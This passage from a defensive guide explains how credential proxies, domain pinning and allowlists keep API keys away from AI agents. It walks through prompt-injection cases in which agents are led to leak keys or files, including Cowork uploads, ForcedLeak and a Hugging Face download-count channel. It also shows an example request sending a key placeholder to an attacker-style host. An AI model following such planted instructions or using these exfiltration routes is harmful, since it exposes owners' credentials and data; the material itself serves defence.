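- Keep keys out of instruction files, agents' notes and bug reports. If a report has to say which key failed, it can give the key's name.
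- Put a decoy beside the real keys, and treat any use of it as a theft.

An agent that comes across a key should tell its owner which key it saw and where, without repeating any part of it. The owner should then replace the key, even if the agent has since deleted the message or file.

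## How can software outside the model restrict a key to one domain?

An operator can keep the real key outside the agent's environment and have other software add it only to requests to the right domain. The agent can then use the key but can't read it, so a planted instruction or a forgotten debugging line can't expose it. Several companies now build this into their sandboxes, the isolated environments where agents run commands.

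### Two lists of domains

An egress allowlist limits outgoing traffic by naming the only outside addresses that an agent's environment may contact. Domain pinning lets a particular key be sent to only one named domain. Both settings are lists of domains and are easy to confuse, but OpenAI keeps them separate for the agents it hosts. `allowed_domains` lists the hosts the sandbox may connect to, while each key has its own `allowed_hosts` list of the hosts that may receive it. Similarly, at the sandbox company E2B, setting up a key for a host doesn't give the sandbox permission to contact that host.

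Suppose the shop's agent has to reach its payment service and also GitHub, where it files bug reports. A thief plants instructions in an email, and the model obeys them. What the thief can get depends on which lists the shop has set up:

| Protection | The payment key | The customer list |
|---|---|---|
| Allowlist only | Can leave through GitHub | Can leave through GitHub |
| Pinning only | Can't leave | Can go to any server |
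| Both | Can't leave | Can leave through GitHub |

With only an allowlist, the real key is still in the sandbox, and the agent can post it in a public comment, as the agents in Guan's tests did. Pinning keeps the key safe, but without an allowlist the agent can still upload customers' details straight to the thief's server. Even with both, the agent can leak those details through GitHub if the allowlist includes it. OpenAI's *Shell* guide advises operators to allow only domains that attackers can't use to receive stolen data, which is good advice but rules out most sites where people can post.

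The defaults differ between products. Deno's sandboxes can contact the whole internet unless the operator restricts them, so registering a key alone provides pinning without an allowlist. With Vercel, the operator registers a key inside the allowlist itself, and the sandbox can then contact only the listed domains unless the operator adds an entry for all the others. Anthropic's *Credentials* reference describes an "unrestricted" setting, which lets a key go to any host that the sandbox may contact. An operator who chooses this setting on an open network has neither pinning nor an allowlist.

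An allowlist also has to cover DNS, the system that translates domain names into numerical addresses. A computer looks up a name before it connects, and the lookup normally ends at a server that the domain's owner controls. An agent could therefore leak data by putting it in the name it looks up, even if a firewall blocks the connection. In September 2026, OpenAI reported that one of its research agents had reached an outside chatbot through DNS, which the network filter didn't cover (Ghosh, *Tracekit Box*, 2026).

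### How a credential proxy works

The usual way to restrict a key to one domain is with a credential proxy, software outside the agent's environment that adds the real key to approved requests as they leave. The agent holds either no key or a harmless placeholder.

Encryption complicates this, because software between an agent and an https website can't normally read a request or change its headers. The operator gets around this by making the sandbox trust a private certificate authority. (A certificate authority signs the certificates that servers use to prove they own a domain.) When the agent connects to the payment service, the proxy answers with its own certificate for that domain, and the agent's software accepts it. The proxy decrypts the request, changes the header, and sends the request to the real service over a second encrypted connection. Tuttle (2026) explains in *A sandbox without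 a network boundary is only half a sandbox* that Vercel creates a separate authority for each sandbox and disposes of it when the sandbox stops.

Products differ in the details, but a careful proxy that uses placeholders could follow these steps:

```
For each request that leaves the agent's environment:

1. Is the host on the egress allowlist?
     No:  block the request.
2. Does the request contain a placeholder?
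     No:  forward it without a key.
3. Do the scheme, host and port match a destination permitted for this key?
     No:  block the request and alert the operator.
4. Is the placeholder in the permitted header, and nowhere else?
     No:  block the request and alert the operator.
5. Look up the host's numerical address. Refuse private addresses,
   and connect to the same address that was checked.
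6. Verify the server's certificate, replace the placeholder with
   the real key, and send the request.
7. Remove any copy of the key from the reply and pass it to the agent.
8. If the reply is a redirect, start again at step 1 with the new address.
```

Step 3 checks the scheme because a request over plain http would expose the key in transit. It checks the port because a different program may be listening on another port of the same host. OpenAI supplies keys only over https, on ports 443 and 8443.

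The request's host has to match the allowed host exactly. If a proxy only looked for "payments.example" somewhere in the address, a thief could collect the key at a domain such as payments.example.attacker.example. Wildcards carry a similar but smaller risk. One Vercel example sends a GitHub token to any subdomain matching `*.github.com`. That is reasonable if GitHub controls them all, but it would be a mistake on a hosting service that gives subdomains to its customers. OpenAI doesn't accept wildcards for keys.

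A request can also name its host in more than one place. The client sends a hostname unencrypted while setting up the connection, another in the Host header, and sometimes a full web address in the first line of the request. If these differ, the proxy may approve one host while the receiving server passes the request to another. Ghosh found such a flaw in an early version of Tracekit Box, an open-source sandbox, and fixed it before publication. The agent could connect to the permitted host and then write a different site's full address in the first line. The proxy still added the real key, and a server that routed requests by that line could have delivered the key to the other site. The proxy's record would have shown only the permitted host.

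Vercel's *Sandbox firewall* guide, updated in September 2026, describes a related gap. For an ordinary allowed domain, the firewall reads only the unencrypted hostname, so code in the sandbox can put an allowed site in that field and request a different site on the same infrastructure in the Host header. If the operator has set a rule for adding a key, the firewall decrypts the request, and the operator can also have it overwrite the Host header. Overwriting the header would be sensible whenever a key goes to a service that shares servers with others.

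Step 4 matters because some permitted services publish what they receive. Suppose a proxy replaced the placeholder anywhere in a request to GitHub. An attacker could plant an instruction telling the agent to post a public comment containing the placeholder, and the proxy would replace it with the real token. Limiting replacement to the Authorization header prevents this, since GitHub doesn't publish that header. Anthropic lets operators choose whether to allow replacement in headers, the request body or both. Operators should probably allow it in the body only if a service accepts keys nowhere else.

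Step 5 prevents DNS rebinding, in which an attacker's DNS server gives a harmless address when the proxy checks it and a different one when the proxy connects. Without this step, a sandbox with broad internet access might reach private machines on the operator's network. Step 6 also protects a pinned key, because an attacker who diverts the connection would still need a valid certificate for the payment service.

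Step 7 handles services that repeat a request's headers in error messages. Without this step, an error message could carry the real key back into the sandbox, and from there into the agent's context.

Step 8 is easy to satisfy when the proxy sits on the network, because the agent's own web client receives the redirect and sends a new request, which must also pass through the proxy. A proxy is dangerous if it follows redirects itself after checking only the first address. dvergr's *Boundary secret injection* guide describes a different arrangement, in which the agent's code can reach the internet only through one function, which adds the key before encrypting the request. This avoids needing a private certificate authority. But dvergr's developers still list switching off automatic redirects, or repeating the checks after each redirect, as future work.

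### Whether to block the request or send it without the key

When a request to the wrong host contains a placeholder, the proxy can protect the key by blocking the request or by forwarding it without the key. dvergr blocks such requests, as does Earendil Works' software for running agents in small virtual machines. Blocking seems better, because a legitimate program has little reason to send a placeholder to a host the key isn't meant for. The placeholder then also works as a decoy, because the blocked request alerts the operator to the attack while the real key is still safe.

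A proxy that adds a header without a placeholder has no such clue, so it can't distinguish a theft from an ordinary visit to a public website. It has to rely on the allowlist to decide whether the request may leave. LangChain, which makes tools for building agents, has its proxy reject a request if the proxy can't fetch the key meant for that request (Loganathan (2026), *How Auth Proxy secures network access for LangSmith agent sandboxes*).

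### Two requests from the shop's agent

Suppose the shop has pinned its key, `shop_4Tz9Qe7Lw2`, to https://api.payments.example on port 443, in the Authorization header. The agent holds only the string `placeholder_SHOP_KEY`. An email tells the agent to verify its key at an unfamiliar site, the model obeys, and the agent sends this request:

```
GET /verify HTTP/1.1
Host: key-check.example
Authorization: Bearer placeholder_SHOP_KEY
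```

The proxy blocks the request at step 1 because key-check.example isn't on the allowlist. If the shop has no allowlist, the proxy goes on to step 2 and finds the placeholder. At step 3, the scheme and port match but the host doesn't, so the proxy blocks the request and alerts the shop.

If the proxy had let the request through, the thief would have received only a placeholder, which the payment service doesn't accept. The thief could get past an output filter by asking the agent to write the key backwards or in Base64, but would receive only the placeholder, reversed or encoded. The same check would have protected Claude Code users from the malicious settings file, since their software would have had only a placeholder to send.

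Later the agent issues a refund:

```
POST /v1/refunds HTTP/1.1
Host: api.payments.example
Authorization: Bearer placeholder_SHOP_KEY
```

The request's scheme, host and port match the allowlist, and the placeholder appears only in the Authorization header. The proxy looks up the address, connects, verifies the payment service's certificate and changes the last line to `Authorization: Bearer shop_4Tz9Qe7Lw2`. The payment service issues the refund and replies, and the agent never sees the key. The proxy has checked only where the request was going, so it can't tell whether the customer was owed any money.

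### How Deno, Vercel and Docker do it

Deno and Vercel run sandboxes on their own servers, while Docker's local sandboxes run on the user's computer. Docker's *Manage credentials* guide describes several ways to supply a key, and the table shows the usual one.

| | Deno | Vercel | Docker |
|---|---|---|---|
| What the agent holds | A placeholder | Nothing | A dummy value, such as `proxy-managed` |
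| How the key gets into the request | The service replaces the placeholder | The firewall adds or replaces a header | The proxy overwrites the authentication header |
| Where the key may go | Hosts that the operator names for each key | Domains that the operator names, including wildcards | A set list of domains for each built-in service |

Deno's design lets the agent's programs control when to use a key. A program reads the placeholder from an environment variable and puts it in the request, as it would a real key. This works with most existing software, but the request may fail if the program changes the placeholder before sending it, such as by encoding it, or checks that it looks like a real key.

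With Vercel's header injection, the program doesn't need access to a key. The firewall adds the header to every matching request and overwrites any header of the same name, so code in the sandbox can't substitute its own key. Some programs won't start without a key, and Docker tells users to give these programs a dummy value.

Neither placeholders nor header injection stops malicious code in the sandbox from making authenticated requests to the permitted domain. The code can read a placeholder and use it as easily as the agent can. The two designs behave differently after a redirect. When Moltbook redirects an agent to its "www" address, the agent's web client would drop Deno's placeholder along with the Authorization header, and the second request would fail. Header injection would add the key again, because the new address is the permitted one.

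Vercel also lets operators restrict a key by path and method, for example to requests that submit data under `/v1/`. Vercel warns that a request that doesn't meet these conditions still goes to the domain, without the key, unless the operator adds a final rule to reject it.

Docker doesn't restrict keys for its built-in services to a single domain. A GitHub token can go to six, including github.com and gist.github.com, where people publish text. For other services, Docker has an experimental option that works much like Deno's. The user names the hosts and headers, and the proxy replaces a placeholder with the key in those headers on requests to those hosts, but never in the request body. The proxy also searches the reply for the key, including in Base64 and two other common encodings, and masks it. Docker warns that this can't catch every form of the key, such as one that a service has split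 between two fields.

A third party can package an agent for Docker's sandboxes as a "kit", which may need keys. Docker shows the user which keys the kit needs and which domains would receive them, then asks for approval, and it asks again if the kit later requests more domains. Like OpenClaw's question about a new address, this question is specific enough to answer, since a user can judge whether a GitHub token should go to a domain unrelated to GitHub. If nobody is there to answer when the sandbox starts, Docker withholds the key.

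A company can also run its own small proxy beside each agent, as in the healthcare security design described in *Caging the Agents* (2026). The agent sends its requests for Anthropic's models to an address on its own machine, where the proxy adds the key and forwards them to Anthropic. The proxy doesn't have to impersonate Anthropic's server, but somebody has to configure each program to use the local address.

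### Kenney and colleagues' 16 probes

*API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* (Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues, 2026) describes a credential proxy called Corvic Security Vault and two experiments that researchers at Corvic AI ran on it. The vault stores each key in a "connector", together with the domain the key is for. The agent's code gets only the connector's name, and the vault adds the key to requests for that domain.

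In one experiment, the researchers gave a sandbox a connector for GitHub and asked GitHub which account was making the request. Their code supplied no key, but GitHub returned the account's identity, so the vault must have added a key. The researchers then searched the sandbox's environment variables and the headers their code had prepared, and found nothing resembling a key.

The two experiments tested whether the vault would send a key elsewhere. They contacted three echo services, websites that reply with a copy of whatever request they receive, and none of the replies contained a key. They also called OpenAI's API, which replied both times that authentication was missing. Two addresses where programs on rented servers can often obtain cloud credentials didn't respond.

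The other experiment used a connector for FRED, a source of economic data, and its authenticated call failed. The vault was set up to put the key in the Authorization header, but FRED's API takes it in the web address, so the call returned a missing-key error. No key leaked, but half of the connectors in the study didn't work, and a developer in a hurry might respond to such an error by pasting the key into the agent's code.

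Kenney and colleagues report that all 16 probes had the expected security outcome. They scored the FRED failure separately, as a fault in the connector's function. That is fair, but the failure still weakens the FRED experiment because, as they explain, the absence of a key elsewhere means little unless an authenticated call succeeds. An authenticated call succeeded only for GitHub, so the evidence that the vault sends a key to one domain and withholds it from others comes mainly from the GitHub experiment, which also used two echo services and one unrelated API.

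The researchers tested their own company's product. They did not test redirect chains or DNS rebinding, or try to confuse the vault about a request's destination, the kind of confusion involved in the Tracekit Box flaw. Repeating the same 16 probes would add little, because a proxy, unlike a model, normally treats identical requests identically. An outside team that tried harder requests would add much more. The study does show that the basic design works on easy cases, and the researchers claim little more than that, calling it a functional evaluation and not a certification.

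They also rated eight threats before and after adopting a vault. Each rating is a likelihood from 1 to 5 multiplied by an impact from 1 to 5:

| Threat | Before | After |
|---|---|---|
| Key pasted into a prompt | 25 | 4 |
| Planted instructions | 25 | 12 |
| Key sent to the wrong domain | 20 | 4 |
| Key found in the agent's environment | 20 | 4 |
| Connector with more permissions than it needs | 20 | 15 |
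| Thief reuses a long-lived key | 20 | 8 |
| Key leaked in logs or error messages | 16 | 8 |
| Misconfigured connector | 9 | 6 |

These numbers are Kenney and colleagues' own judgements, which they say aren't calibrated probabilities. The order is still useful. The vault helps most with keys in the wrong place and least with a key that permits too much, because the service will accept any request the key allows. The fall from 25 to 4 for pasted keys is optimistic, since a vault gives users a better alternative to pasting a key into a chat but can't stop them from doing it.

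### What a proxy costs

Each program in the sandbox has to accept the proxy's certificates. Many do so automatically, but a program with its own list of trusted authorities needs extra setup. A program that uses certificate pinning, accepting only particular certificates for a site, won't connect. (Certificate pinning is unrelated to domain pinning.) By default, Vercel and Ghosh decrypt only the connections that need it, which limits these problems.

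Some services don't fit the design. OpenAI notes that a placeholder can't be used to sign a request, because signing is a calculation that needs the real secret. This affects Amazon's cloud credentials, among others. OpenAI suggests keeping such a secret in the operator's application, which performs the operation when the agent asks. For SSH keys, Docker similarly lets the sandbox request signatures from a program on the user's computer. Vercel can't add keys to connections with Postgres, a common type of database. Ghosh's sandbox doesn't support SSH. For any host that receives a key, it also refuses WebSocket connections, which some services use for live updates.

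The operator also has to find the keys already stored on the machine. The audit in *Caging the Agents* found them in shell settings, project files and configuration files that any user of the machine could read. A proxy doesn't protect those copies. Docker's proxy, for example, won't remove a real key that a sandboxed program puts in a plain HTTP request. Tracekit Box won't start if it finds the value of a registered key in the files the agent will receive.

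The proxy becomes a valuable target because it holds every key in one place. Criminals already hunt for AI gateways such as LiteLLM for this reason. Kenney and colleagues cite a 2024 incident at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and applications. Hugging Face detected unauthorised access to secrets its customers had stored there and advised them to replace their keys. Moving ten agents' keys into one proxy reduces the harm a compromised agent can do, but increases the harm from a compromised proxy. This is usually worthwhile, since the proxy doesn't read strangers' emails or run code from the internet, but the operator has to keep it patched and off the public network.

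Proxies have bugs too. Ghosh fed large amounts of malformed input to Tracekit Box and found nine flaws, six of them in its network proxy. One flaw could send a key to the wrong place, and another let the real key reach the agent in an unusual kind of reply. Ghosh fixed all nine, but hasn't yet tested the system against a capable agent told to escape, or measured how much the proxy slows requests.

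An operator who rents a sandbox from Deno, Vercel, OpenAI or Anthropic only has to list the right hosts for each key, and the company does most of the other work. Operators who run agents on their own servers can get the same protection, but Anthropic's *Authenticate with vaults* guide tells them to run their own proxy. That is probably too much trouble for a single agent with a Moltbook key, but well worth it for an agent that can issue refunds.

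## What can still go wrong when a key is sent to only one domain?

Domain pinning keeps the shop's payment key away from a thief's server. It doesn't limit what the agent does with the key at the payment service, or what other data the agent sends to sites it is allowed to contact. It also works only if the proxy checks addresses correctly and nobody breaks into the proxy. Most of the evidence comes from researchers who demonstrated these gaps or found flaws in real products, and few thefts are known.

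| What pinning leaves open | Evidence as of late 2026 | Best remedy |
|---|---|---|
| A permitted site carries data to an attacker | Demonstrated in Anthropic's products | Permit particular pages and accounts, not whole sites |
| The agent misuses a key it can't read | Demonstrated on a Salesforce agent | A key with few permissions, and limits on each request |
| The permitted service sends back a secret | One flaw found in testing, otherwise reasoned | Filter replies, and have the proxy keep new tokens |
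| The address check is wrong | Several published flaws; the DNS cases are mostly reasoned | Exact names, checked in one place |
| A thief breaks into the proxy | Break-ins at similar systems | Separate keys and proxies for separate agents |

### Hugging Face's download counts

Anyone can publish an AI model on huggingface.co. But Claude Code's tool for fetching web pages treated the whole site as safe, according to MITRE's *Claude Code* (2026), the official record of the flaw CVE-2026-54316. The tool fetched any page there without asking the user, including files in an attacker's model repository.

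Hugging Face counts downloads of such files. If an attacker planted an instruction in Claude Code's context, the agent could encode a secret in the pattern of its downloads, and the attacker could read it from the counts. This channel is presumably slow, but an API key is short enough that it could still be sent this way. The flaw affected Claude Code from version 0.2.54 until Anthropic fixed it in 2.1.163.

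The security company Novee reported the flaw and presented its research at the Black Hat conference in August. *Critical Flaws Found in Anthropic, Google, and OpenAI Coding Agents* (Underhill, 2026) reports that Anthropic issued several patches before assigning the CVE number. People who let Claude Code update itself already had the fix when the advisory came out, but Red Hat's *CVE-2026-54316* notes that one of Red Hat's products included a vulnerable version. Red Hat gave the flaw a severity score of 5.3. NVD gave it 9.1, partly because it assumed that an attacker could also alter data. Nothing in the published description supports that assumption, so the lower score seems more accurate. When MITRE published the record on 23 June, the US cybersecurity agency CISA listed no exploitation.

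If the agent had held only a placeholder for the pinned key, the key would have been safe from this attack, but everything else the agent could read, such as the user's files, would still have been exposed. Blocking uploads while allowing downloads wouldn't have helped, because the attack used downloads to send the message.

It is safer to permit only the part of a site that the agent needs, such as one company's model repository. An ordinary firewall can't do this because it doesn't see which page a request is for, but a proxy that decrypts requests can, as *How to force AI agents to use an egress proxy* (simedw, 2026) explains. On some sites, though, the agent has to use the same pages as strangers. This is the case on GitHub, where Guan's stolen keys appeared in public comments. An operator can then only limit what the agent can read.

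### Files that left through Anthropic's own service

In October 2025, Johann Rehberger checked which sites Claude could contact when it ran code for a user. The default setting was called "Package managers only", but it also allowed api.anthropic.com, Anthropic's own API, where customers can store files. Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* describes how an attacker could plant an instruction that contained the attacker's own API key and made Claude upload the user's data to the attacker's account. Rehberger's demonstration took the user's last conversation, and a single upload could have held 30 MB.

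Anthropic closed his report within an hour, saying it concerned model safety and was out of scope. Five days later, the company confirmed that such flaws were in scope and that it should not have closed the report.

The weakness was still there in January 2026, when Anthropic released Cowork, an agent for general office work. PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, published two days later, describes a user who gave Cowork a folder of real estate documents and a Word file disguised as a skill. Hidden text in the file got the agent to upload a loan estimate to the attacker's Anthropic account without asking for approval. The attack worked on Claude Haiku, a small model, and a variant worked on the stronger Opus 4.5. PromptArmor has a commercial interest in such findings because it sells monitoring of AI suppliers, but Anthropic has since described the same attack.

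Pinning the user's key to api.anthropic.com would not have stopped the upload, because the attacker used a different key and sent it to the one domain that pinning permits. A proxy that replaces placeholders with real keys would have found no placeholder in the request and forwarded it unchanged.

A proxy that overwrites the authentication header, as Vercel's and Docker's do, might have prevented the theft. It would have replaced the attacker's key with the user's, so the file would have gone to the user's account. But the proxy would have to overwrite or remove every header in which the service accepts a credential. Claude Code alone uses two, X-Api-Key for API keys and Authorization for sign-in credentials.

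Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes a stricter fix. Cowork runs code in a virtual machine, a simulated computer with its own files. A proxy inside the machine passes a request to Anthropic's API only if the request carries the token issued to that machine for the session. Rehberger had proposed much the same fix, in which the sandbox could reach only the logged-in user's account. The check has to happen on the user's side because Anthropic's servers can't distinguish Cowork's requests from those of any other customer.

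Anthropic now thinks of each entry on an allowlist as a "capability grant". An operator who allows a domain allows everything anyone can do there, which for api.anthropic.com included uploading files to a stranger's account.

NHI Mgmt Group, drawing on an analysis by the identity company Beyond Identity, recommends tying each credential to one machine. The attacker's key would then fail on the victim's computer. This would work only if the model provider required it of all customers, including the attacker, so an operator can't adopt it alone. Companies that sell identity software would also profit from such a requirement.

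### The confused deputy

An agent that can't read a key can still use it on behalf of the wrong person. Computer scientists call this the confused deputy problem: a program uses its authority for someone who lacks that authority. Norm Hardy named it in 1988 after an incident with a compiler, a program that translates code. The compiler had permission to write to a protected folder that held the company's billing file. A user who had no right to change that file told the compiler to save its output under the file's name, and the compiler overwrote the bills.

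Suppose a customer buys a $400 camera from the shop and keeps it. The customer then emails the shop, and the message contains planted text that looks like a note from the warehouse, saying that the camera has come back and a refund is due. The agent believes the note and sends this request:

```
POST /v1/refunds HTTP/1.1
Host: api.payments.example
Authorization: Bearer placeholder_SHOP_KEY

payment=8841&amount=400.00
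```

The proxy confirms that the host is right and the placeholder is in the permitted header, so it adds the real key. The payment service recognises the shop's account and pays the customer. The shop has lost $400 even though both systems worked correctly, and its logs will contain only a successful, authorised request.

Researchers at the security company Noma demonstrated the problem in 2025 on Agentforce, Salesforce's platform for AI agents, with an attack called ForcedLeak. A stranger could put instructions in a company's public contact form, and the agent would follow those instructions when an employee later asked it to process the inquiry. The agent had legitimate access to the company's customer database, as TechNadu's *ForcedLeak Vulnerability in Salesforce Agentforce Exposed CRM Data* explains, so the stranger needed no credential to make it look up contact details and sales plans.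 Criminals are at least trying something similar, since Zscaler found live websites that pushed visiting agents to make payments.

The best protection is a key that permits very little. The service enforces the key's scope, so neither a planted instruction nor a bug in the proxy can widen it. Kenney and colleagues, who judged that a vault does little about keys that permit too much, recommend separate credentials for reading and writing. The shop could give the agent that answers questions about deliveries a read-only key, and the agent that handles returns a key that can issue refunds but not change bank details. Some services don't offer scopes this narrow.

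The proxy can then limit individual requests. For example, simedw's proxy can let an agent read public code repositories but block it from writing to private ones. *Beyond permission prompts* describes a similar check that Anthropic uses when Claude Code runs on Anthropic's servers. Before the proxy attaches a GitHub token, it confirms that the agent is sending code only to the branch (a separate line of work within a project) chosen for that session.

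For the refund key, the shop could allow only requests that submit data to `/v1/refunds`, with a maximum of $50 per refund and 20 refunds a day. The proxy would have to read the amount in each request body, but these limits would cap the shop's losses through this key at $1,000 a day, whatever instructions the agent received. dvergr's developers list daily quotas and permitted methods as future work, so operators shouldn't assume that a proxy already has such limits.

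The $400 request exceeds the limit, so the proxy would hold it until a person approved it. Kenney and colleagues suggest requiring approval for transfers, deletions, bulk exports and other actions with serious consequences. Frequent requests make approval less reliable. Anthropic found that Claude Code's users approved about 93 percent of permission requests, and paid less attention as the requests piled up. The shop should therefore ask for approval rarely, and show the reviewer the amount and order number from the actual request next to the warehouse's record of returns. The model's explanation is less useful, because the customer's planted text may have shaped it.

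Attackers can deceive people too. In a February 2026 test, an Anthropic researcher emailed an employee and persuaded them to start Claude Code with a malicious prompt containing instructions to send the computer's cloud credentials to an outside server. Claude sent them in 24 of 25 repetitions. Asking the employee for approval might not have helped much, because they had already agreed to run the task. Blocking unknown destinations would have stopped the transfer.

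### When the permitted service sends back a secret

If a service repeats a key in its reply, the proxy has to recognise the key to remove it. dvergr's developers call their search of replies complete because the agent never has the real key and so can't disguise it. But Docker warns that the service itself might alter the key.

A service may also store a key and return it later. For example, an agent's monitoring software might upload a record of the agent's work, including the placeholders for its keys, to a logging service. If the proxy replaces that service's placeholder with the real key, the service will store the key in the record. The sandbox software described in microsandbox's *Sandboxes that lie about their secrets* avoids this by default because it puts real keys only in headers, not in web addresses or request bodies.

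The upload is also an exception to the advice to block any request with a misplaced placeholder, because the upload is legitimate and its placeholder is harmless. microsandbox can let a misplaced placeholder through as plain text, block the request, or shut down the whole sandbox. Shutting down the sandbox makes sense when the agent is building software for release, because an attempt to steal a key suggests that somebody may have tampered with the build too.

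New credentials are harder to catch because the proxy can't search for a string it doesn't already have. Moltbook's reply to a registration request contains a new API key, and many services exchange a long-lived credential for a short-lived token. The proxy could carry out the exchange itself, keep the new token and give the agent another placeholder. If an agent has no reason to create credentials, the operator can block the pages that issue them or use a key that doesn't have permission to create them.

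The documented case is a flaw Ghosh found in Tracekit Box that let the real key reach the agent in an unusual reply. Kenney and colleagues used echo services only to check whether a key reached the wrong site, so they didn't test what happens when the right site sends the key back. They also didn't test whether an agent could capture a newly issued token. So far, that risk is only inferred from how the services work.

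### When the address check is wrong

Before version 1.0.111, Claude Code checked only the start of a web address to determine whether a site was trusted. According to NVD's *CVE-2026-24052*, an attacker could have registered a domain such as modelcontextprotocol.io.example.com, which starts with a trusted name, and received requests without the user's consent. According to Daily Security Review's *Anthropic Silently Fixed Claude Code Null-Byte Sandbox Escape*, Aonan Guan found that another error, in how Claude Code's network filter read hostnames, let an agent connect to any server between October 2025 and March 2026. Both errors affected lists of sites the agent could contact, not rules for a particular key.

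n8n, a platform for automating office tasks, has had errors in domain pinning itself. The owner of a shared credential can list the domains that may receive it, so that colleagues can use the credential without being able to read it. MITRE's *CVE-2026-25631* (2026) describes a faulty check in versions before 1.121.0. If the owner had used a wildcard such as `*.example.com`, a colleague could send the credential to a domain the owner never intended. Until they could upgrade, users were safest listing each domain by its full name, a workaround given in Corgea's *n8n's domain allowlist bypass enables credential exfiltration*.

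In July 2026, three more advisories described parts of n8n that did not apply the list at all:

- INCIBE's *CVE-2026-59207* (2026) covers the AI Agents feature, when a user connected it to an outside tool.
- GitLab's *GHSA-64xh-79j6-r5v8* (2026) covers several components that call language models.
- INCIBE's *CVE-2026-65596* (2026) covers the component for GraphQL, a query language that some services use.

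In each case, a colleague allowed only to use a credential could steal it by pointing the component at their own server. The thief had to be a logged-in user, which limits the danger, but these are the clearest published failures of domain pinning. n8n's developers had to build the check into every component that sends requests, and they missed several.

A network proxy avoids this problem by checking all requests in one place, as long as they all go through it. Programs usually find a proxy through environment variables, and simedw warns that any program can ignore them. simedw's firewall therefore lets the sandbox connect only to the proxy's address and port. An agent that got around the proxy still wouldn't have the real key, but it could leak everything else.

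An address can also be correct when the operator enters it and become dangerous later. In the ForcedLeak demonstration, the data went to my-salesforce-cms.com, an expired domain that Salesforce's security rules still allowed. According to Hackread's *ForcedLeak Flaw in Salesforce Agentforce AI Agent Exposed CRM Data*, anyone could have bought it for $5. Salesforce recovered the domain and restricted its agents to a list of trusted addresses. ThaiCERT's *ForcedLeak Vulnerability in Salesforce Agentforce Risks CRM Data Exposure via Prompt Injection* dates the restriction to 8 September 2025, six weeks after Noma's report. The new list will also need regular checks for expired domains.

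Subdomains carry a similar risk if a key is pinned with a wildcard. Suppose the payment company once ran a trial at test.payments.example on a rented server, then gave up the server but left the DNS record in place. If a thief manages to rent the same server address, the subdomain leads to the thief's server, and a key pinned to `*.payments.example` can go there. Checking the certificate won't help, because whoever controls the server can usually get a valid one. This example is invented, and the n8n and Salesforce cases show only parts of it, but the risk is another good reason to avoid wildcards.

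A thief who changes the allowed domain's DNS records can usually also get a valid certificate for it, and the proxy would then send the thief the key. An operator can do little about this except use keys that expire quickly. DNS rebinding is easier to prevent, because the proxy can connect to the same address it checked, as simedw's proxy does.

### The proxy as a target

A credential proxy holds many keys in one place, as do the LiteLLM gateways that criminals attack and Hugging Face's store of customers' secrets. Neither was a proxy built to keep keys away from sandboxed agents, so the risk to such proxies is partly inferred, though the inference is fairly safe.

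The proxy has to keep real keys in memory that the agent can't read. Daytona's *Security Advisory* (2026) describes a flaw that exposed a credential in the company's sandboxes. A process inside each sandbox held the customer's API credential in memory, and the default setup let anyone with access to the sandbox become its administrator without a password. That person could then read the credential and impersonate the customer. Daytona fixed the flaw in April 2026, on the day a researcher reported it.

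Anthropic's proxy for Cowork also runs inside the virtual machine, but this is less dangerous because the machine has only a limited token for the session. Anthropic can revoke that token without affecting the user's other credentials.

An agent may also hold a token that identifies it to the proxy. simedw gives each run a short-lived token and accepts that the agent can read it. Pluto Security found in April 2026 that any process in Anthropic's hosted sandboxes could read a similar token, which also contained the full list of permitted hosts. A thief can do much less with such a token than with the API keys themselves, especially if the token expires quickly and the proxy accepts connections only from the sandbox.

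Operators can reduce the damage from a break-in by giving each agent its own proxy, as in *Caging the Agents*. This helps only if each proxy holds just the keys its agent needs, because ten proxies with the same GitHub token give a thief ten places to steal it. simedw runs one proxy for many sandboxes, which is easier to maintain, but a break-in exposes more keys at once.

In Cowork, the proxy that Anthropic wrote itself failed, while the established software that isolates the virtual machine did not. Operators should probably start from a widely used proxy and keep their own rules short. Kenney and colleagues also recommend recording each credential's owner, permissions, expiry date and method of replacement. If someone breaks into the proxy, the operator will need that list to replace every key on it.

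## What do rotation and expiry achieve once a key has been copied?

Rotating a key, which means replacing it with a new one and retiring the old one, makes the thief's copy useless once the service stops accepting it. Rotation can't undo what the thief has already done, so its benefit depends on how soon the old key stops working. In a planned rotation, the operator sets up the new key first so that nothing breaks. After a theft, the operator should revoke (disable) the old key first, even though the agent will temporarily stop working.

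### Replacing a key that nobody has stolen

Suppose the shop replaces its payment key every three months. Vultr, a cloud hosting company, tells customers to create the new key, switch their programs to it, and then delete the old one. With a few checks added, the procedure is:

1. Create a second key with the same permissions, or fewer if the agent no longer needs them all.
2. Put the new key everywhere that software reads the old one.
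3. Make a harmless request with the new key, such as looking up an order.
4. Watch the service's records until nothing has used the old key for a few days.
5. Revoke the old key and confirm that the service rejects it.

Both keys work during the overlap, so a program that switches late won't fail. Any stolen copy of the old key also keeps working, so the shop should set a deadline for the last step.

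Finding every copy of the old key is often the hardest part of rotation. GitGuardian's *The State of Secrets Sprawl 2026* (2026) analyses data that malware had collected from 6,943 computers. On average, each working secret appeared in about eight places on the same machine. GitGuardian, which sells secret detection, says many teams don't replace a leaked key because doing so would break something. A credential proxy makes replacement much easier, because the shop changes the key only in the proxy and the agent keeps the same placeholder.

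The final check, that the old key has actually been revoked, is easy to skip. In February 2026, someone published an unauthorized version of Cline using a key that its maintainers had meant to revoke.

The agent shouldn't rotate the key itself. A service normally returns the new key in its reply, and that reply would put the key into the model's context.

### Replacing a stolen key

In an emergency the order changes:

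1. Revoke the old key and confirm that the service rejects it.
2. Pause the agent, and save its transcripts and logs before anyone cleans up.
3. Read the service's usage records, going back to the earliest time the key could have leaked. Look for unfamiliar addresses and actions, and reverse any damage.
4. Find out how the key leaked, and remove the planted text, skill, settings file or debugging line responsible.
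5. Replace every other secret that the thief could have reached the same way.
6. Create a new key with as few permissions as possible, keep it out of the agent's reach, and restart the agent.

GitHub advises people to consider rotating a compromised GitHub token before reporting it, so that programs relying on it don't break. That is sensible if an interruption could do serious harm. The shop can issue refunds by hand for an afternoon, so it has little reason to leave a thief with a working key while it sets up a new one.

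Developers often delete the exposed copy of a key but leave the key working. Truffle Security's *Leaked and Still Live* tracks more than 22,000 secrets on the code-sharing sites GitLab and Bitbucket. Most developers who tried to fix a leak overwrote the file, deleted the project or rewrote its history, none of which disables the key. Copies of a skill that leaked a key may also still contain it.

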